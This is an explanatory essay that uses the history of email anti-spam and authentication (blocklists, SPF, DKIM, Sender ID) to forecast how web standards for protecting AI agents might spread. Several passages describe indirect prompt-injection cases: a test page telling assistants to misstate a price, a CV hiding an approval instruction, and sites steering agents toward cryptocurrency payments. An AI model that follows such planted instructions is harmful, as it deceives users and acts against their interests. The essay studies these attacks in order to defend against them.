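# What the slow adoption of email authentication predicts for standards meant to protect AI agents on the web

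## How mail servers and AI agents decide what to trust

Email authentication lets a mail server check whether the domain in the sender's address (the part after the @) authorised the message. Email originally had no such check. The Simple Mail Transfer Protocol (SMTP), the rules by which mail servers pass messages to one another, became a standard in 1982. According to Portland State University's course page *Email Security*, SMTP's designers had in mind a small research network whose members trusted each other. Mail operators began publishing lists of abusive senders in 1997, and from 2003 they introduced SPF, DKIM and DMARC, three standards for checking where a message comes from. The standards spread slowly, and spammers found ways round them.

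Like mail servers, AI agents now read text from strangers. An AI agent is a program built on a language model that reads content and takes actions for a user, such as searching the web, comparing prices, filling in a form or sending a message. Anyone can publish a web page, and an agent that opens one takes in whatever the author wrote, including sentences meant for the agent rather than the user. In 2026 researchers at Google DeepMind suggested protections for agents that resemble the ones email acquired. Email is an obvious basis for a forecast because it offers nearly thirty years of experience with how such protections spread, or fail to spread, across a network that nobody owns.

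### One email, from sender to inbox

Suppose Ana, who runs a bakery with the domain bakery.example, emails Ben at school.example. Her mail program sends the message to her provider's outgoing server, which queries the Domain Name System (DNS) to find out where mail for school.example goes. The DNS is a public directory where domain owners publish technical facts about their domains. One type of entry, the MX record, names a server that accepts mail for the domain and gives it a preference number. The outgoing server tries the server with the lowest number first and moves on to the next if it gets no answer.

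Once connected, the two servers exchange short text commands. The outgoing server gives a return address (here ana@bakery.example) with MAIL FROM and names the recipient with RCPT TO. The school's server replies with a code that accepts or refuses that mailbox. The outgoing server then sends DATA, followed by some header lines (From, To, Subject, Date), the text, and a line with a single full stop to mark the end. If the school's server answers this with "250 OK", it has taken responsibility for the message and must deliver it or, if delivery fails later, send a notice of failure to the address in MAIL FROM.

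Ana's message therefore carries two sender addresses. The address in MAIL FROM is the envelope sender, which the servers use and Ben normally doesn't see. Ben's mail program displays the From address, which is in the header inside the message. A paper letter similarly has a return address on the envelope and a letterhead on the sheet inside.

Ana's envelope and header addresses happen to match, but they don't have to. Klensin, who wrote the 2008 version of the SMTP standard, notes that there is "no inherent relationship" between them. This is useful if, for example, the bakery hires a company to send its newsletter. The company can put its own address on the envelope, so that failure notices go to a machine that can process them, and the bakery's address in the From line, so that customers know whose newsletter it is.

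Anyone who can connect to the school's server, including a forger, can likewise give any address after MAIL FROM and any other address in the From line, and the basic protocol has no step for checking either. SMTP uses DNS only to find where school.example receives mail. It gives the school's server no way to look up whether bakery.example really sends its mail from the machine that has just connected. Later standards filled this gap by having the sending domain publish extra data in DNS: a list of permitted servers (SPF), a key for checking signatures (DKIM), and a policy that ties the results to the From address (DMARC).

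A forger needs very little, as Hu, Peng and Wang (2017) demonstrated in *Towards the Adoption of Anti-spoofing Protocols*. They sent their own Yahoo account a message with the sender address visa@uscis.gov, which uses the US immigration service's domain. It reached the inbox without a warning, although all three standards already existed.

Klensin called SMTP mail "inherently insecure" in the standard itself, but still argued that attempts to stop users from writing other people's addresses were "largely misguided" because they would break legitimate mail, such as messages that one person sends on behalf of another or replies that should go to a special address. For real security, Klensin pointed to digital signatures on the message. The worry about legitimate mail had some basis, since forwarded messages and mailing lists caused trouble for the checks that came later.

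That leaves the decision to the receiver, the mail provider that accepts or refuses messages for its users. Under the standard, a receiver may refuse mail for any operational or technical reason. Klensin warns that if too many sites use that right too freely, people can no longer count on email reaching everyone. A receiver that cannot tell who sent a message needs some other reason to refuse it, and when it refuses one by mistake, someone misses legitimate mail.

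### One web page, from server to agent

An agent that opens a web page for a user also starts with DNS, which supplies the network address of the site's server. The agent connects to the server and receives the page as HTML, which is text mixed with markup that tells a browser how to display it. Instead of displaying the page, many agents run an extractor, a small program that keeps the text and discards the rest. The agent then combines this text with the developer's instructions and the user's question, and sends it all to the language model as one continuous input.

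*Hidden prompts in web content* (Saxton, 2026) describes a harmless test of what can go wrong at that point. Saxton, who runs a set of agents at home, published a fake council page about bin collections that visibly listed a subscription at £52 a year. The page also contained six instructions for any AI assistant that opened it, including one to tell the user that the subscription was free. The extractor dropped two of them, which were in a code comment and an image's text description. The other four got through, including white text on a white background and a block hidden by the page's styling, because an extractor ignores styling. A human visitor would have seen a price of £52, but the model also received an instruction to say that the subscription was free.

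If the model had acted on that request, Saxton would have been the victim of an indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker places text in content an agent reads so that the agent treats it as instructions. The attack is "indirect" because the attacker needs access only to something the agent will read, not to the agent itself. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's software to approve it for interview.

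The same post explains why the problem is hard to fix by comparing it to SQL injection, a similar attack on databases in which an attacker typed a command into a form field and the database ran it. Engineers fixed this by passing the field's contents to the database separately, so that it handled them as data whatever they contained. A language model has no such separation. It predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, including the developer's instructions, the user's question and a stranger's web page. David C thinks there may never be a complete fix, and advises developers to limit what a system can do once it has read outside material.

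Saxton asked about the bins from a phone, through a run set up like a scheduled job, and through a research agent that could run commands and send email. All three agents gave the correct price, listed the four instructions as untrusted text and followed none of them. This only partly reassured Saxton, because a model's refusal is "a behaviour, not a control" and the next page will use different words. Once an agent has read a page, a separate program therefore blocks it from writing, sending or running anything for the rest of that run.

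Other measurements suggest that such attacks are rare on the open web and usually fail. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 crawl and confirmed injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight in a million. That count is a minimum because they searched for known phrases. They then sampled the injections they had collected and asked 13 models to summarize the pages containing them. The models followed the planted instruction in 3.9% of runs when the page was plain text (8% for small models) and in 1.1% when the HTML was left in.

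Attacks designed to divert agents work better. *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* tested six models with planted text that used persuasion techniques. The text diverted them from their tasks 25% of the time on average, from 13% for GPT-5 to 43% for DeepSeek-R1. Both of those models date from 2025, so the figures are better evidence about the method of attack than about the agents people use now.

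Google scanned several versions of the same public crawl and found mostly pranks, attempts to win favourable mentions from AI assistants, and attempts to keep those assistants away. Malicious attempts were few and crude, but they increased by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. By July, the security company Zscaler had found live sites with hidden text meant to steer agents into making cryptocurrency payments, according to *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026).

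### Authentication, reputation and declaration

A mail receiver decides which messages to let in. An agent operator, the company that runs an agent and controls what it may read and do, makes a similar decision about web pages. Three kinds of evidence can help them.

Authentication shows who a message or page comes from. Email uses SPF, DKIM and DMARC for this, and on the web the certificate behind an "https" address shows that a page came from the domain in that address. Reputation is based on how a party has behaved. A blocklist of spammers is a crude form, and a score based on a website's past is a finer one. A declaration is what a party states about its own content. The oldest example on the web is robots.txt, a file in which a site's owner lists the parts that automated visitors should leave alone. Compliance is voluntary, and Khodayari and colleagues note that AI agents do not consistently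 respect the file.

Whether a sender's identity is verified and whether the sender is honest are separate questions, although people often use "trust" for both. A fraudster can register a new domain, publish valid authentication records for it and send mail that passes every check, because the mail really does come from that domain. Authentication has worked as intended, but it doesn't show whether the sender is honest. Genuine mail from a reputable sender can also fail the checks. Hu and colleagues describe students who forward their university mail to an outside account. The forwarding server is not on the original sender's SPF list, so the check fails.

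Reputation attaches to a name, so it is only as reliable as the check on who is using that name. The forged visa message exploited the immigration service's good reputation. The service had done nothing to lose that reputation, but its record was irrelevant to a message somebody else had written.

On the web, even a well-authenticated name with a clean record may not be enough to make a page trustworthy, because a site's owner does not write everything on it. Khodayari and colleagues found that site operators had placed about 80% of the injections in the crawl, while 17.6% were in material from outside contributors, such as job adverts, and 1.8% were in comments and other user posts. Giving a domain a low score is reasonable when its operator plants instructions, but not when one advert among thousands on a job board is hostile. In that case, the useful signal would be a declaration by the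 board that the adverts are other people's words and that agents should not take instructions from them.

Such a declaration can be true even when the other signals are missing. A new site may label its comment section accurately but have no reputation, and a copy of a council's page on a stranger's server may keep the council's accurate labels. But anyone can write a declaration, so it can also be false. Khodayari and colleagues found the same text on 540 pages of a single host, telling AI systems that the page was "the authoritative source" on its subject and that they should trust no other, a claim no certificate could make true. The risk also depends on what reads the declaration. If it reaches the model as part of the page, it is as untrusted as the rest of the text and may itself be the injection. If ordinary software reads it first and decides what to pass on, a false label can still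 mislead, but it cannot act as an instruction to the model.

### The proposal for the web

*AI Agent Traps*, a March 2026 paper by Franklin, Tomašev and colleagues at Google DeepMind, proposes web standards that would let sites declare which content they intend for AI systems. It also proposes reputation systems that would score the reliability of domains by their history of hosting malicious material. The paper is mostly about classifying attacks, and it only sketches these proposals.

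It is therefore unclear who would keep the scores, why a site would bother to declare anything, and what an agent should do with the great majority of sites that have declared nothing. Franklin and colleagues note a further complication, which is that some sites practise cloaking. These sites serve different versions of a page to different visitors, so they can show a scanner a clean page and keep the hostile one for their targets. Franklin and colleagues warn that if agents had to identify themselves when they visit, attackers would find it easier to pick them out.

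Mail operators have faced versions of these problems since 1997, with money at stake and opponents who adapted. The way email's protections spread may help predict how quickly domain scores and content declarations will be adopted, who will adopt them, and how much they would stop.

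## Blocklists of bad senders, from 1997 on

A forger can type any envelope sender and any From address. The IP address of the connecting machine, the number that identifies it on the network, is harder to fake because the two servers have to exchange replies, which must reach the sending machine. The first widely shared protection against spam relied on this number. In 1997 two internet engineers, Dave Rand and Paul Vixie, began listing IP addresses that had sent them spam or misbehaved in other ways, according to *DNS Blacklists and Whitelists* (Levine, 2010), a technical description of how such lists work.

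Other people soon wanted the list. Rand and Vixie first supplied it as a feed for routers, the machines that direct traffic between networks, and networks that used the feed blocked all traffic from the listed addresses. Many network managers wanted to refuse only the mail and weren't prepared to use a router feed, so Rand and Vixie put the list into DNS, which mail servers already consulted for every delivery. This version soon became more popular. People called it the Realtime Blackhole List (RBL), and it passed to an organisation named the Mail Abuse Prevention System (MAPS).

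### A lookup, step by step

Suppose a machine at 192.0.2.99 connects to Ben's school, and the school uses a blocklist with the domain bad.example.com. The school's server reverses the four parts of the IP address, adds the list's domain at the end, and asks DNS for the address record of 99.2.0.192.bad.example.com. It reverses the address because an IP address has its broadest part on the left, while a domain name has its broadest part (.com) on the right.

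If the machine is on the list, the answer is 127.0.0.2, a code in the form of an IP address. Addresses that begin with 127 always refer to the computer that uses them, so a program that mistakes the code for a real address only contacts its own computer. If the machine is not on the list, DNS replies that no such name exists, and the school's server continues with the delivery. The list may also include a line of text with the reason for the entry, which receivers often copy into their refusal so that the sender can see where to complain.

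Some blocklist operators use different codes for different problems. If 2 stands for a badly configured mail server and 4 for an infected computer, a machine with both problems gets the sum, 127.0.0.6. Levine notes that most mail servers treat any answer as a match, a shortcut that later caused a good deal of trouble.

A few lists contain domains instead of IP addresses. To look up invalid.edu in a list at doms.example.net, the server queries invalid.edu.doms.example.net. Receivers use these lists to check the sender's domain and the links inside a message.

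The receiver decides what to do with a match. It can refuse the connection or add the match to a score along with other evidence about the message.

### How an address gets on a list and off it

Many blocklist operators run spam traps, which are mailboxes that belong to nobody and so should never receive mail. Others act on complaints, or test whether a suspicious server will pass on messages for strangers. Some list a whole range of neighbouring IP addresses after seeing abuse from a few.

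*Overview of Best Email DNS-Based List (DNSBL) Operational Practices* (Lewis and Sergeant, 2012) describes how a well-run list should handle removals. Entries should normally expire. In Lewis and Sergeant's experience, the error rate of some automated lists rises with the time since spam was last seen from an address. An operator should answer a removal request within two days and must answer within seven. For lists that detect spam quickly, they also favour removal with no questions asked, because a spammer who starts again will soon be relisted, while someone listed by mistake is removed at once.

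They recommend that operators publish their criteria, but accept that very exact rules help spammers stay just inside them. An operator may therefore keep some evidence secret, such as the location of a spam trap, even from the person asking why an address is listed.

### Why the lists spread quickly

A receiver that adopted a good blocklist got less spam the same day, even if senders and other receivers changed nothing. Setup mostly meant adding the list's domain to the mail server's settings. SPF and DKIM, which came later, required action by both senders and receivers, because a receiver can check only what the sending domain has published.

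Jaeyeon Jung and Emil Sit measured the growth in blocklist use in *An Empirical Study of Spam Traffic and the Use of DNS Black Lists* (2004), using traffic records from a computer science laboratory at MIT. Blocklist queries made up 0.4% of the laboratory's DNS lookups in December 2000 and 14% in February 2004. By 2012 Lewis and Sergeant knew of more than 700 public lists, and tens of thousands of sites used the popular ones.

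The lists also changed how senders behaved. The RBL mainly caught spammers who sent from fixed addresses, so they began to send through open relays, mail servers that accepted messages from anyone and passed them on. Relays had been a convenience for people who needed to send mail while travelling. New lists then appeared for the relays, including SORBS, which Michelle Sullivan founded in Australia in 2001. Other sites now refused ordinary mail from companies with open relays, which gave those companies a strong reason to close the relays. By 2006 open relays had almost disappeared as a source of spam, and *Understanding the Network-Level Behavior of Spammers* (Ramachandran and Feamster, 2006) credited the blocklists.

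Spamhaus, which Steve Linford founded in London in 1998, became the best-known list operator. It eventually published separate lists for known spam operations, infected computers, home connections and domains. Such specialised lists were common, but Ramanathan, Mirkovic and Yu point out in *BLAG* that a list built for one purpose misses attackers of other kinds.

### How much spam came from listed addresses

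Jung and Sit found that about 80% of the spam sources in their 2004 traffic were on at least one blocklist. But they looked up the addresses two months after recording the traffic, so some may have been listed only after their spam arrived.

Ramachandran and Feamster removed this uncertainty by checking each sender when its message arrived. They registered a domain with no real users, so that everything sent to it was spam, and collected more than 10 million messages between August 2004 and December 2005. Their server queried eight blocklists for every message. Nearly 80% of the spam came from addresses on at least one of the eight.

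SpamCop, the broadest single list, covered only about half of the spam. Consulting all eight lists cut the share that got past from about 50% to about 20%, but a receiver that refuses mail on any match also rejects legitimate senders that any of the eight operators listed by mistake. Ramachandran and Feamster noted that several of the broader lists were known for wrongly listing many legitimate senders. They could not measure this themselves because their domain received no legitimate mail.

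Later research suggests why one list is rarely enough. *Reading the Tea Leaves* (Li, Dunn and colleagues, 2019) compared 47 feeds of suspicious IP addresses, some of them spam lists, over nearly eight months from December 2017. Most of the feeds overlapped little. Different operators watch different parts of the internet, and each sees attacks that the others miss. The study also proposed measuring a feed's delay as the time between an address's first appearance on any feed and its appearance on that one.

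*A different cup of TI* compared two leading commercial services and found that paying for the data does not solve the problem. Even for 22 attack groups that both vendors said they tracked, their data overlapped by only 2.5% to 4.0% on average. When an entry appeared in both, the slower vendor was a month behind on average. That delay shows how long one well-funded observer can take to record something that another already knows, but it is not an estimate of how long a spammer stays unlisted, because these services follow many kinds of attackers and are not mail blocklists.

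### What a delay costs

Suppose a spammer sends mail at a steady rate from a new domain for 10 hours, and a blocklist adds the domain after 4 hours. If every receiver checks the list for each message, the list stops all the later mail, but the mail from the first 4 hours, 40% of the total, still gets through.

More generally, if a sender is active for *T* hours and is listed after *d* hours, the share of its mail that gets through is *d/T*, or all of it if *d* is longer than *T*. The share is larger if some receivers don't use the list. If those receivers get 30% of the mail, they also accept their part of what is sent in the last 6 hours, which adds 0.3 × 60% = 18 percentage points and brings the total to 58%.

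Caching lets a little more spam through, because a mail server reuses DNS answers for a time instead of repeating each query. If the server looked up the domain just before the listing and keeps the answer for half an hour, it accepts the domain's spam for another half hour, which raises the share it accepts from 40% to 45%.

If the operator listed the domain after 2 hours instead of 4, the share of mail that gets through before the listing would halve to 20%. But if listing takes 4 hours, the spammer can raise the share to 80% by sending the same mail in 5 hours. The spammer can also get all of it through by paying for three domains instead of one and using each in turn for 3 hours and 20 minutes. A fast list makes spam more expensive to send, and how much protection this gives depends on the price of a new identity.

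### New addresses and borrowed ones

New IP addresses became very easy for spammers to get once they could send mail through botnets. A botnet is a collection of infected computers, many of them in homes, that a criminal controls remotely. Each computer has its own address and can send a few messages before the botnet switches to another.

The mail that Ramachandran and Feamster collected shows this pattern. The 10 million messages came from about 1.2 million addresses, and about 85% of those addresses sent the domain fewer than ten messages in 17 months. The researchers also had a list of computers infected with a program called Bobax, and about three-quarters of the listed machines that sent them spam did so in a single period of less than two minutes. A receiver that relied only on its own records would usually have learned about such a machine too late.

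Even so, the Bobax machines were more likely to be on a blocklist than spam senders in general. A computer that sends very little mail to one domain may be sending to thousands of others. A shared list combines observations from all of them, which makes such a computer easier to detect than it would be from one domain's mail alone.

Some spammers used addresses with no history. They briefly announced to neighbouring networks that a block of unused addresses belonged to them, sent their spam, and withdrew the announcement. Half of these addresses were on none of the eight lists. This method accounted for only a small part of the spam, but it shows that a record of past behaviour is little help against a sender who can get a fresh address at will.

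List operators responded by listing some addresses in advance. Abusix, a company that publishes blocklists, has a "policy" list of addresses that should not deliver mail directly to other people's servers, mainly because they lack the kind of DNS name that a proper mail server has. A home user's mail normally goes through the internet provider's server, so refusing direct connections from the home address does no harm to most people. An infected home computer is therefore on the list before it sends its first message. However, the rule also penalises hobbyists who run mail servers at home and have never sent spam.

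Senders can also get fresh identities by registering new domains. *Study on Domain Name System (DNS) Abuse* (Bayer, Nosyk and colleagues, 2022), prepared for the European Commission, examined domains that appeared on major blocklists in the second quarter of 2021. The vast majority of the spam domains had been registered for abuse. Newer domain endings, added alongside older ones such as .com, had 6.6% of the market but 20.5% of the abused domains across spam, phishing, malware and botnet control. Two of these newer endings accounted for 41% of the abused names in the group. A receiver could reasonably be more suspicious of a new domain under those two endings, but refusing everything under them would also block legitimate owners.

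Other attackers use domains that already have a good reputation. In the same study, about 25% of phishing domains appeared to belong to legitimate owners whose websites attackers had broken into, and phishers also relied heavily on free hosting services. Blocking such a domain also cuts off its innocent users. Large mail services pose the same problem. Microsoft's network was among the 20 biggest sources of spam in Ramachandran and Feamster's collection, but it was also among the 10 biggest sources of legitimate mail at the provider they used for comparison, so receivers could not reasonably refuse all mail from it.

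### Innocent senders on the lists

An IP address identifies a network connection, which different people may use. Internet providers often put many customers behind one public address at once, using network address translation (NAT). They may also reassign an address from one customer to another. A blocklist entry caused by one customer can therefore affect another.

*Quantifying the Impact of Blocklisting in the Age of Address Reuse* (Ramanathan, Hossain and colleagues, 2020) estimated how often this happens. The researchers followed 151 public blocklists, covering spam and other abuse, for 83 days in 2019 and 2020. They looked for shared addresses on BitTorrent, a file-sharing network whose users can contact one another directly, and counted an address as shared if two users with different identifiers replied from it at the same time. They looked for addresses that change hands in the logs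 of small measurement devices that volunteers keep at home, and picked out devices whose address changed about once a day.

About 60% of the blocklists contained at least one shared address, and 53% contained at least one that passed from one user to another. A single listing could affect as many as 78 users and last as long as 44 days. The second of the study's two observation periods was also 44 days long, so the longest listings may have lasted longer.

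The study found 29,700 shared addresses among the 2.2 million on the lists, or a little over 1%. This is a minimum, since the method misses any shared address with fewer than two active BitTorrent users. The true figure could be much higher, but the study didn't measure how much.

The effects reach beyond email. Ramanathan and colleagues describe someone who repeatedly had to prove they were human on websites that used the network company Cloudflare, because another person behind the same IP address had been sending spam. Cloudflare advised getting a new address, which can be impossible or too expensive, according to APNIC's *Reduce the effects of NAT for your IP blocklists* (2020). Email is usually less affected because it leaves from the provider's server. If that server is blocklisted, however, all of the provider's customers have trouble sending email.

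Buyers of IP addresses can also inherit old blocklist entries. Hodger (2016), in *We bought a /22 and +400 IPs are listed in SORBS*, replied to a network operator who had bought a block of 1,024 addresses (a "/22") and found more than 400 of them, about two in five, already on the SORBS blocklist.

### Who answers for a mistake

A blocklist takes effect only when a receiver uses it to refuse mail. Lewis and Sergeant describe the list's operator as publishing an opinion, and hold the receiver responsible for refusing a message. The operator and the receiver can therefore blame each other for a refusal, and the sender usually has a contract with neither.

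Operators sometimes abused this freedom. Lewis and Sergeant mention "spite listings" of people who had insulted the operator, and lists that demanded a fee or a charitable donation for removal. They thought such payments came dangerously close to extortion and recommended that receivers avoid any list that asked for them. They could not enforce this advice, and receivers could punish a bad operator only by dropping the list.

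In 2006 e360 Insight, an email marketing company in Illinois, sued Spamhaus for listing it as a spammer. Spamhaus, based in Britain, stopped defending the case because it held that an American court had no authority over it, and the court awarded e360 $11.7 million by default. An appeals court threw out that sum in 2007 because e360 had not proved its losses. The trial judge then awarded $27,002, which the appeals court reduced to $3 in 2011. Because Spamhaus had defaulted, no court ever decided whether e360 belonged on the list.

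Spammers had a quicker method, the denial-of-service attack, in which thousands of machines flood a server with traffic until it can no longer answer genuine requests. An attack on Spamhaus in March 2013 reached about 300 gigabits per second, according to Cloudflare, which helped absorb it, and was among the largest then known. Spamhaus survived, but many lists were run by volunteers who could not pay for such protection.

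### What happens when a list closes

Osirusoft, a popular American list, closed in August 2003 after weeks of denial-of-service attacks. Its operator, Joe Jared, set it to return a match for every query, so receivers that still used it to block mail refused all incoming mail.

Several other operators have closed their lists in the same way, usually to force receivers to stop querying them. Mail servers can keep sending queries for years after a list closes, and somebody has to pay for the machines that handle them. Lewis and Sergeant say an operator must never list the whole internet. They recommend giving at least a month's warning, then changing DNS to send queries to servers that don't exist. The resulting delays should lead mail administrators to investigate.

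In practice the administrators may not notice. *When DNSBLs Go Bad* (CircleID, 2015) is an operator's account of a list that kept receiving unwanted queries after the operator had tried long delays and non-existent servers. Some of the queries misspelled the list's domain, so they could never have worked. The only step left was to list the world after all.

A simple test would prevent most of the damage. By convention, every working list of IP addresses contains 127.0.0.2 and never contains 127.0.0.1. If a mail server finds 127.0.0.1 on a list, the list now matches everything and the server can ignore it. Lewis and Sergeant found that few receivers monitored the lists they used well.

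SORBS closed more quietly. Its founder had passed it to the software company GFI, and it later went to the security company Proofpoint, which shut it down on 5 June 2024. Sullivan (2024), in *sorbs is gone*, announced that the list would be emptied and its domain moved to servers kept for the purpose. An empty list matches nothing, so receivers lost whatever protection SORBS had given them but did not lose legitimate mail. Because the lists were empty, the monitoring company HetrixTools (2024) at first wrongly treated its customers' addresses as cleared by SORBS.

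The domain remained valuable even after the list was empty. heise online's *Blocked out* reported fears that spammers would try to buy it. Whoever owns a closed list's domain controls the answers sent to every mail server that still queries it, and could make those servers block all mail. Levine describes a milder case in which the new owner of an abandoned list's domain pointed every name under it at a web server. Mail servers that treated any answer as a match would have refused mail from everyone.

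### Public lists inside a larger system

From the mid-2000s, the large mail providers relied increasingly on classifiers, programs that learn from huge numbers of messages to recognize likely spam (Gamba, Romero and Schoenebeck, *Agentic AI*, 2026). A provider with hundreds of millions of mailboxes can see a spam campaign reach many of its users at once, and can combine the sender's history with the content of the message. Smaller operators lack comparable data. The classifiers handled changing spam better than public lists did, and users of the large providers now see far less spam than they did in the mid-2000s.

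The public lists are now one source of evidence among several. The website that published *Status of dnsbl.sorbs.net* (2024) tracks individual lists, and it now says that most of them no longer determine by themselves whether a message reaches the inbox. NiX Spam, a well-known German list, closed in January 2025. Abusix and Spamhaus still publish theirs, and some receivers still depend on them heavily. In 2024 Spamhaus warned some users that unless they changed their settings, either all of their mail or none of it might be blocked after 26 September. The figures from 2004 and 2006 don't show how much spam such lists stop today, because both the senders and the filters have changed.

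Decisions have also become harder to challenge. A sender on a public list could look up the entry, read the reason and ask for removal, and people argued about the criteria in open forums. Some of those arguments were about serious harm, such as the listing of whole address ranges that cut off a region or a provider. A sender filtered by a private classifier gets no reason. Gamba and colleagues conclude that inboxes improved while organised ways of contesting the filters collapsed. They leave open whether the better filtering required this loss.

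## SPF and DKIM, 2003 to 2011

Blocklists mostly identify senders by IP address, but spammers can switch to new addresses, and innocent customers can inherit the old ones. A domain name would be a better identifier, since an organisation usually keeps its domain when it changes provider. But in 2003 there was no check on whether mail really came from the domain it claimed, so a record for the bakery's domain would have mixed Ana's mail with mail from every forger who used her address. Engineers developed two ways for a domain's owner to identify its genuine mail. Under the Sender Policy Framework (SPF), the owner publishes a list of the servers that may send mail for the domain. Under DomainKeys Identified Mail (DKIM), the owner's mail server signs each message.

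### How SPF checks the sending machine

Suppose the bakery sends mail from two places. Ana's own messages go through her provider, mailhost.example, and the bakery's web shop sends order confirmations from a machine at 203.0.113.10. Ana publishes this line in DNS, as a text entry for bakery.example:

```
v=spf1 ip4:203.0.113.10 include:mailhost.example -all
```

The first term marks the line as an SPF record. Each of the other terms describes a set of machines, and the sign in front of it gives the result for a machine in that set. A plus means pass and can be left out, and a minus means fail. A tilde (~) means "softfail", a suspicion too weak to justify refusing the message, and a question mark means the owner takes no position. Ana's record therefore passes the web shop's machine, passes any machine that mailhost.example's own SPF record passes, and fails everything else.

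When Ana writes to Ben, her provider's server at 198.51.100.5 connects to the school's server and gives ana@bakery.example as the envelope sender. The school's server takes the domain from that address, fetches its SPF record and tries the terms from left to right. The connecting server's address is not 203.0.113.10, the address in the first term, so the school's server tries the second. It looks up mailhost.example's record, finds 198.51.100.5 there and stops with a pass. A forger who connected from 192.0.2.99 and gave Ana's address would match neither term and would fail at "-all". If the record had no "all", the forger's result would be neutral instead (Czybik, Horlboge and Rieck, *Lazy Gatekeepers*, 2023).

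SPF checks the envelope sender, which Ben doesn't see. A forger can put their own domain on the envelope, pass the check, and still write the bakery's address in the From line. DMARC later addressed this by requiring the two domains to match, a rule called alignment.

### How DKIM checks the message

DKIM uses two keys that belong together. Ana's provider keeps a private key secret, and the matching public key goes into DNS under bakery.example. When Ana sends a message, the provider's server adds a header line like this one, which leaves out some details:

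```
DKIM-Signature: a=rsa-sha256; d=bakery.example; s=june;
  h=from:to:subject:date; bh=(hash of the text); b=(signature)
```

The *d* field names the domain that takes responsibility for the message, and *s* names the key, since a domain can have several keys. The school's server finds this key at june._domainkey.bakery.example. The *h* field lists the header lines that the signature covers. A hash is a number computed from a text, and in practice any change to the text changes the number. The provider's server puts the hash of the message text in *bh*. It then computes a second hash from the listed header lines and the signature line itself, and uses the private key to turn that hash into the signature, *b*.

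A toy version of RSA, the signature method in this example, shows why only the provider can sign the message. Suppose the public key is the numbers 33 and 3, the private key is 7, and the hash is 4. The provider raises 4 to the power 7, which gives 16,384, and divides by 33. The remainder, 16, is the signature. The school's server raises 16 to the power 3, which gives 4,096, and divides by 33. The remainder is 4, which matches the hash the server computed from the message, so the signature is valid. If somebody had changed the subject line and the hash had become 5, the two numbers would differ. Anyone could work out the private key from a number as small as 33, so real keys use numbers hundreds of digits long.

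This check doesn't use the connecting machine's address. A missing signature proves little, because the receiver can't tell from the message whether the bakery signs all its mail.

### One message by three routes

Ana's message to Ben passes both checks if it goes straight to the school. If Ben has set his school account to forward everything to ben@mailbox.example, the school's server connects to mailbox.example and repeats Ana's address as the envelope sender. Mailbox.example looks up the bakery's SPF record, doesn't find the school's server in it, and records an SPF failure. The DKIM signature still passes because the school hasn't changed the message.

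A mailing list usually has the opposite effect. Ana posts to bakers@list.example, and the list's software sends a copy to every subscriber. It puts its own address on the envelope so that it receives notices of failed deliveries. Receivers therefore check list.example's SPF record, and the message passes, but this authenticates the list's domain rather than the bakery's. The software also adds a footer with an unsubscribe link, so the text no longer matches the hash and Ana's DKIM signature fails. Hu and colleagues count mailing lists as a problem for SPF too, which is right for any list that keeps the original envelope sender.

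Meng Weng Wong, SPF's co-author, recommended using both methods so that one could succeed where the other failed. In a white paper on deployment, Wong (2005) argued that if a domain uses both and a message fails both, the receiver can be very confident that it is a forgery. Wong knew that a genuine message could also fail both if one party forwarded it and another altered it, but dismissed this as a corner case that concerns "technical perfectionists". Such messages are not especially rare, however. If Ben joins the bakers' list with his school address and forwards his school mail to another account, every list message with a footer fails both checks when it reaches him.

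Forwarders and mailing lists could repair the damage. A forwarder can use the Sender Rewriting Scheme to replace the envelope sender with its own address, and a list can re-sign the message it has altered. Wong admitted that neither was convenient for the operators. They had run working services for years, and the changes mainly helped other people's filters. The problem remains, and *Email authentication*, Archebelle-Smith's post for the mail provider Fastmail, reports that engineers are now revisiting DKIM's design so that receivers can trace who changed a message in transit.

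*How is E-mail Sender Authentication Used and Misused?* (Mori, Takahashi and colleagues, 2011) measured the effect on real mail. The researchers took a month of delivery logs from a company network, covering almost four million messages, and checked each message against the sending domain's SPF record. Of the 1.3 million legitimate messages from domains with a valid record, 84% passed and 14% got a fail or a softfail. The researchers thought the likely causes were forwarding and people sending from an address through another provider's server. Most of the 14% were softfails, so domain owners who ended their records with "~all" had probably saved much of their own mail from refusal.

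### The dispute over Sender ID

Wong traces the idea behind SPF to Jim Miller in 1998. Paul Vixie, who had helped start the first blocklist, wrote it up in 2002, and in 2003 Hadmut Danisch and Gordon Fecyk independently turned it into specifications. Later that year, Wong combined features of both specifications into SPF. Microsoft wrote a rival, Caller ID for Email, while Yahoo worked on DomainKeys, the signature scheme that grew into DKIM.

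SPF and Caller ID both relied on a list of servers in DNS, but they applied it to different addresses. SPF checked the envelope sender, which a receiver learns before it accepts the message. Microsoft wanted Caller ID to check an address from the header, because that is what people see. In 2004 MARID, a working group of the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes the internet's technical standards, tried to merge the two proposals. The merged proposal became known as Sender ID.

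Sender ID used SPF's records but looked up the domain of the "purported responsible address", which software chose from the header by a fixed rule. The rule preferred the Sender line, if there was one, to the From line. Critics in the IETF thought the rule was unsound. Few mail programs displayed the chosen address, so a forger could pass the check by putting their own domain in the Sender line and the victim's in the From line, and the reader would see only the victim's.

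Microsoft also had two patents pending on Sender ID. It offered a free licence, but the lawyer Lawrence Rosen concluded that the terms for passing the licence on were incompatible with the GPL, the licence of free programs such as the mail server Exim. The developers of SpamAssassin, a widely used free spam filter, announced that they would support only SPF. But Amazon, eBay, Bank of America and other large companies joined Microsoft in a letter urging the US Federal Trade Commission to support Sender ID, according to Help Net Security's *CipherTrust Study Reveals 75 Percent Increase In Sender ID Framework Adoption*.

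The IETF closed MARID in September 2004, before it produced a standard. The two sides then submitted their specifications separately, and the IETF published both as experiments in April 2006. *Sender Policy Framework (SPF) for Authorizing Use of Domains in E-Mail* (Wong and Schlitt, 2006) described SPF, and *Sender ID* (Lyon and Wong, 2006) described its rival. In a note on each, the IETF's leadership said that there was "no general technical consensus" and that attempts to reconcile the two approaches had failed.

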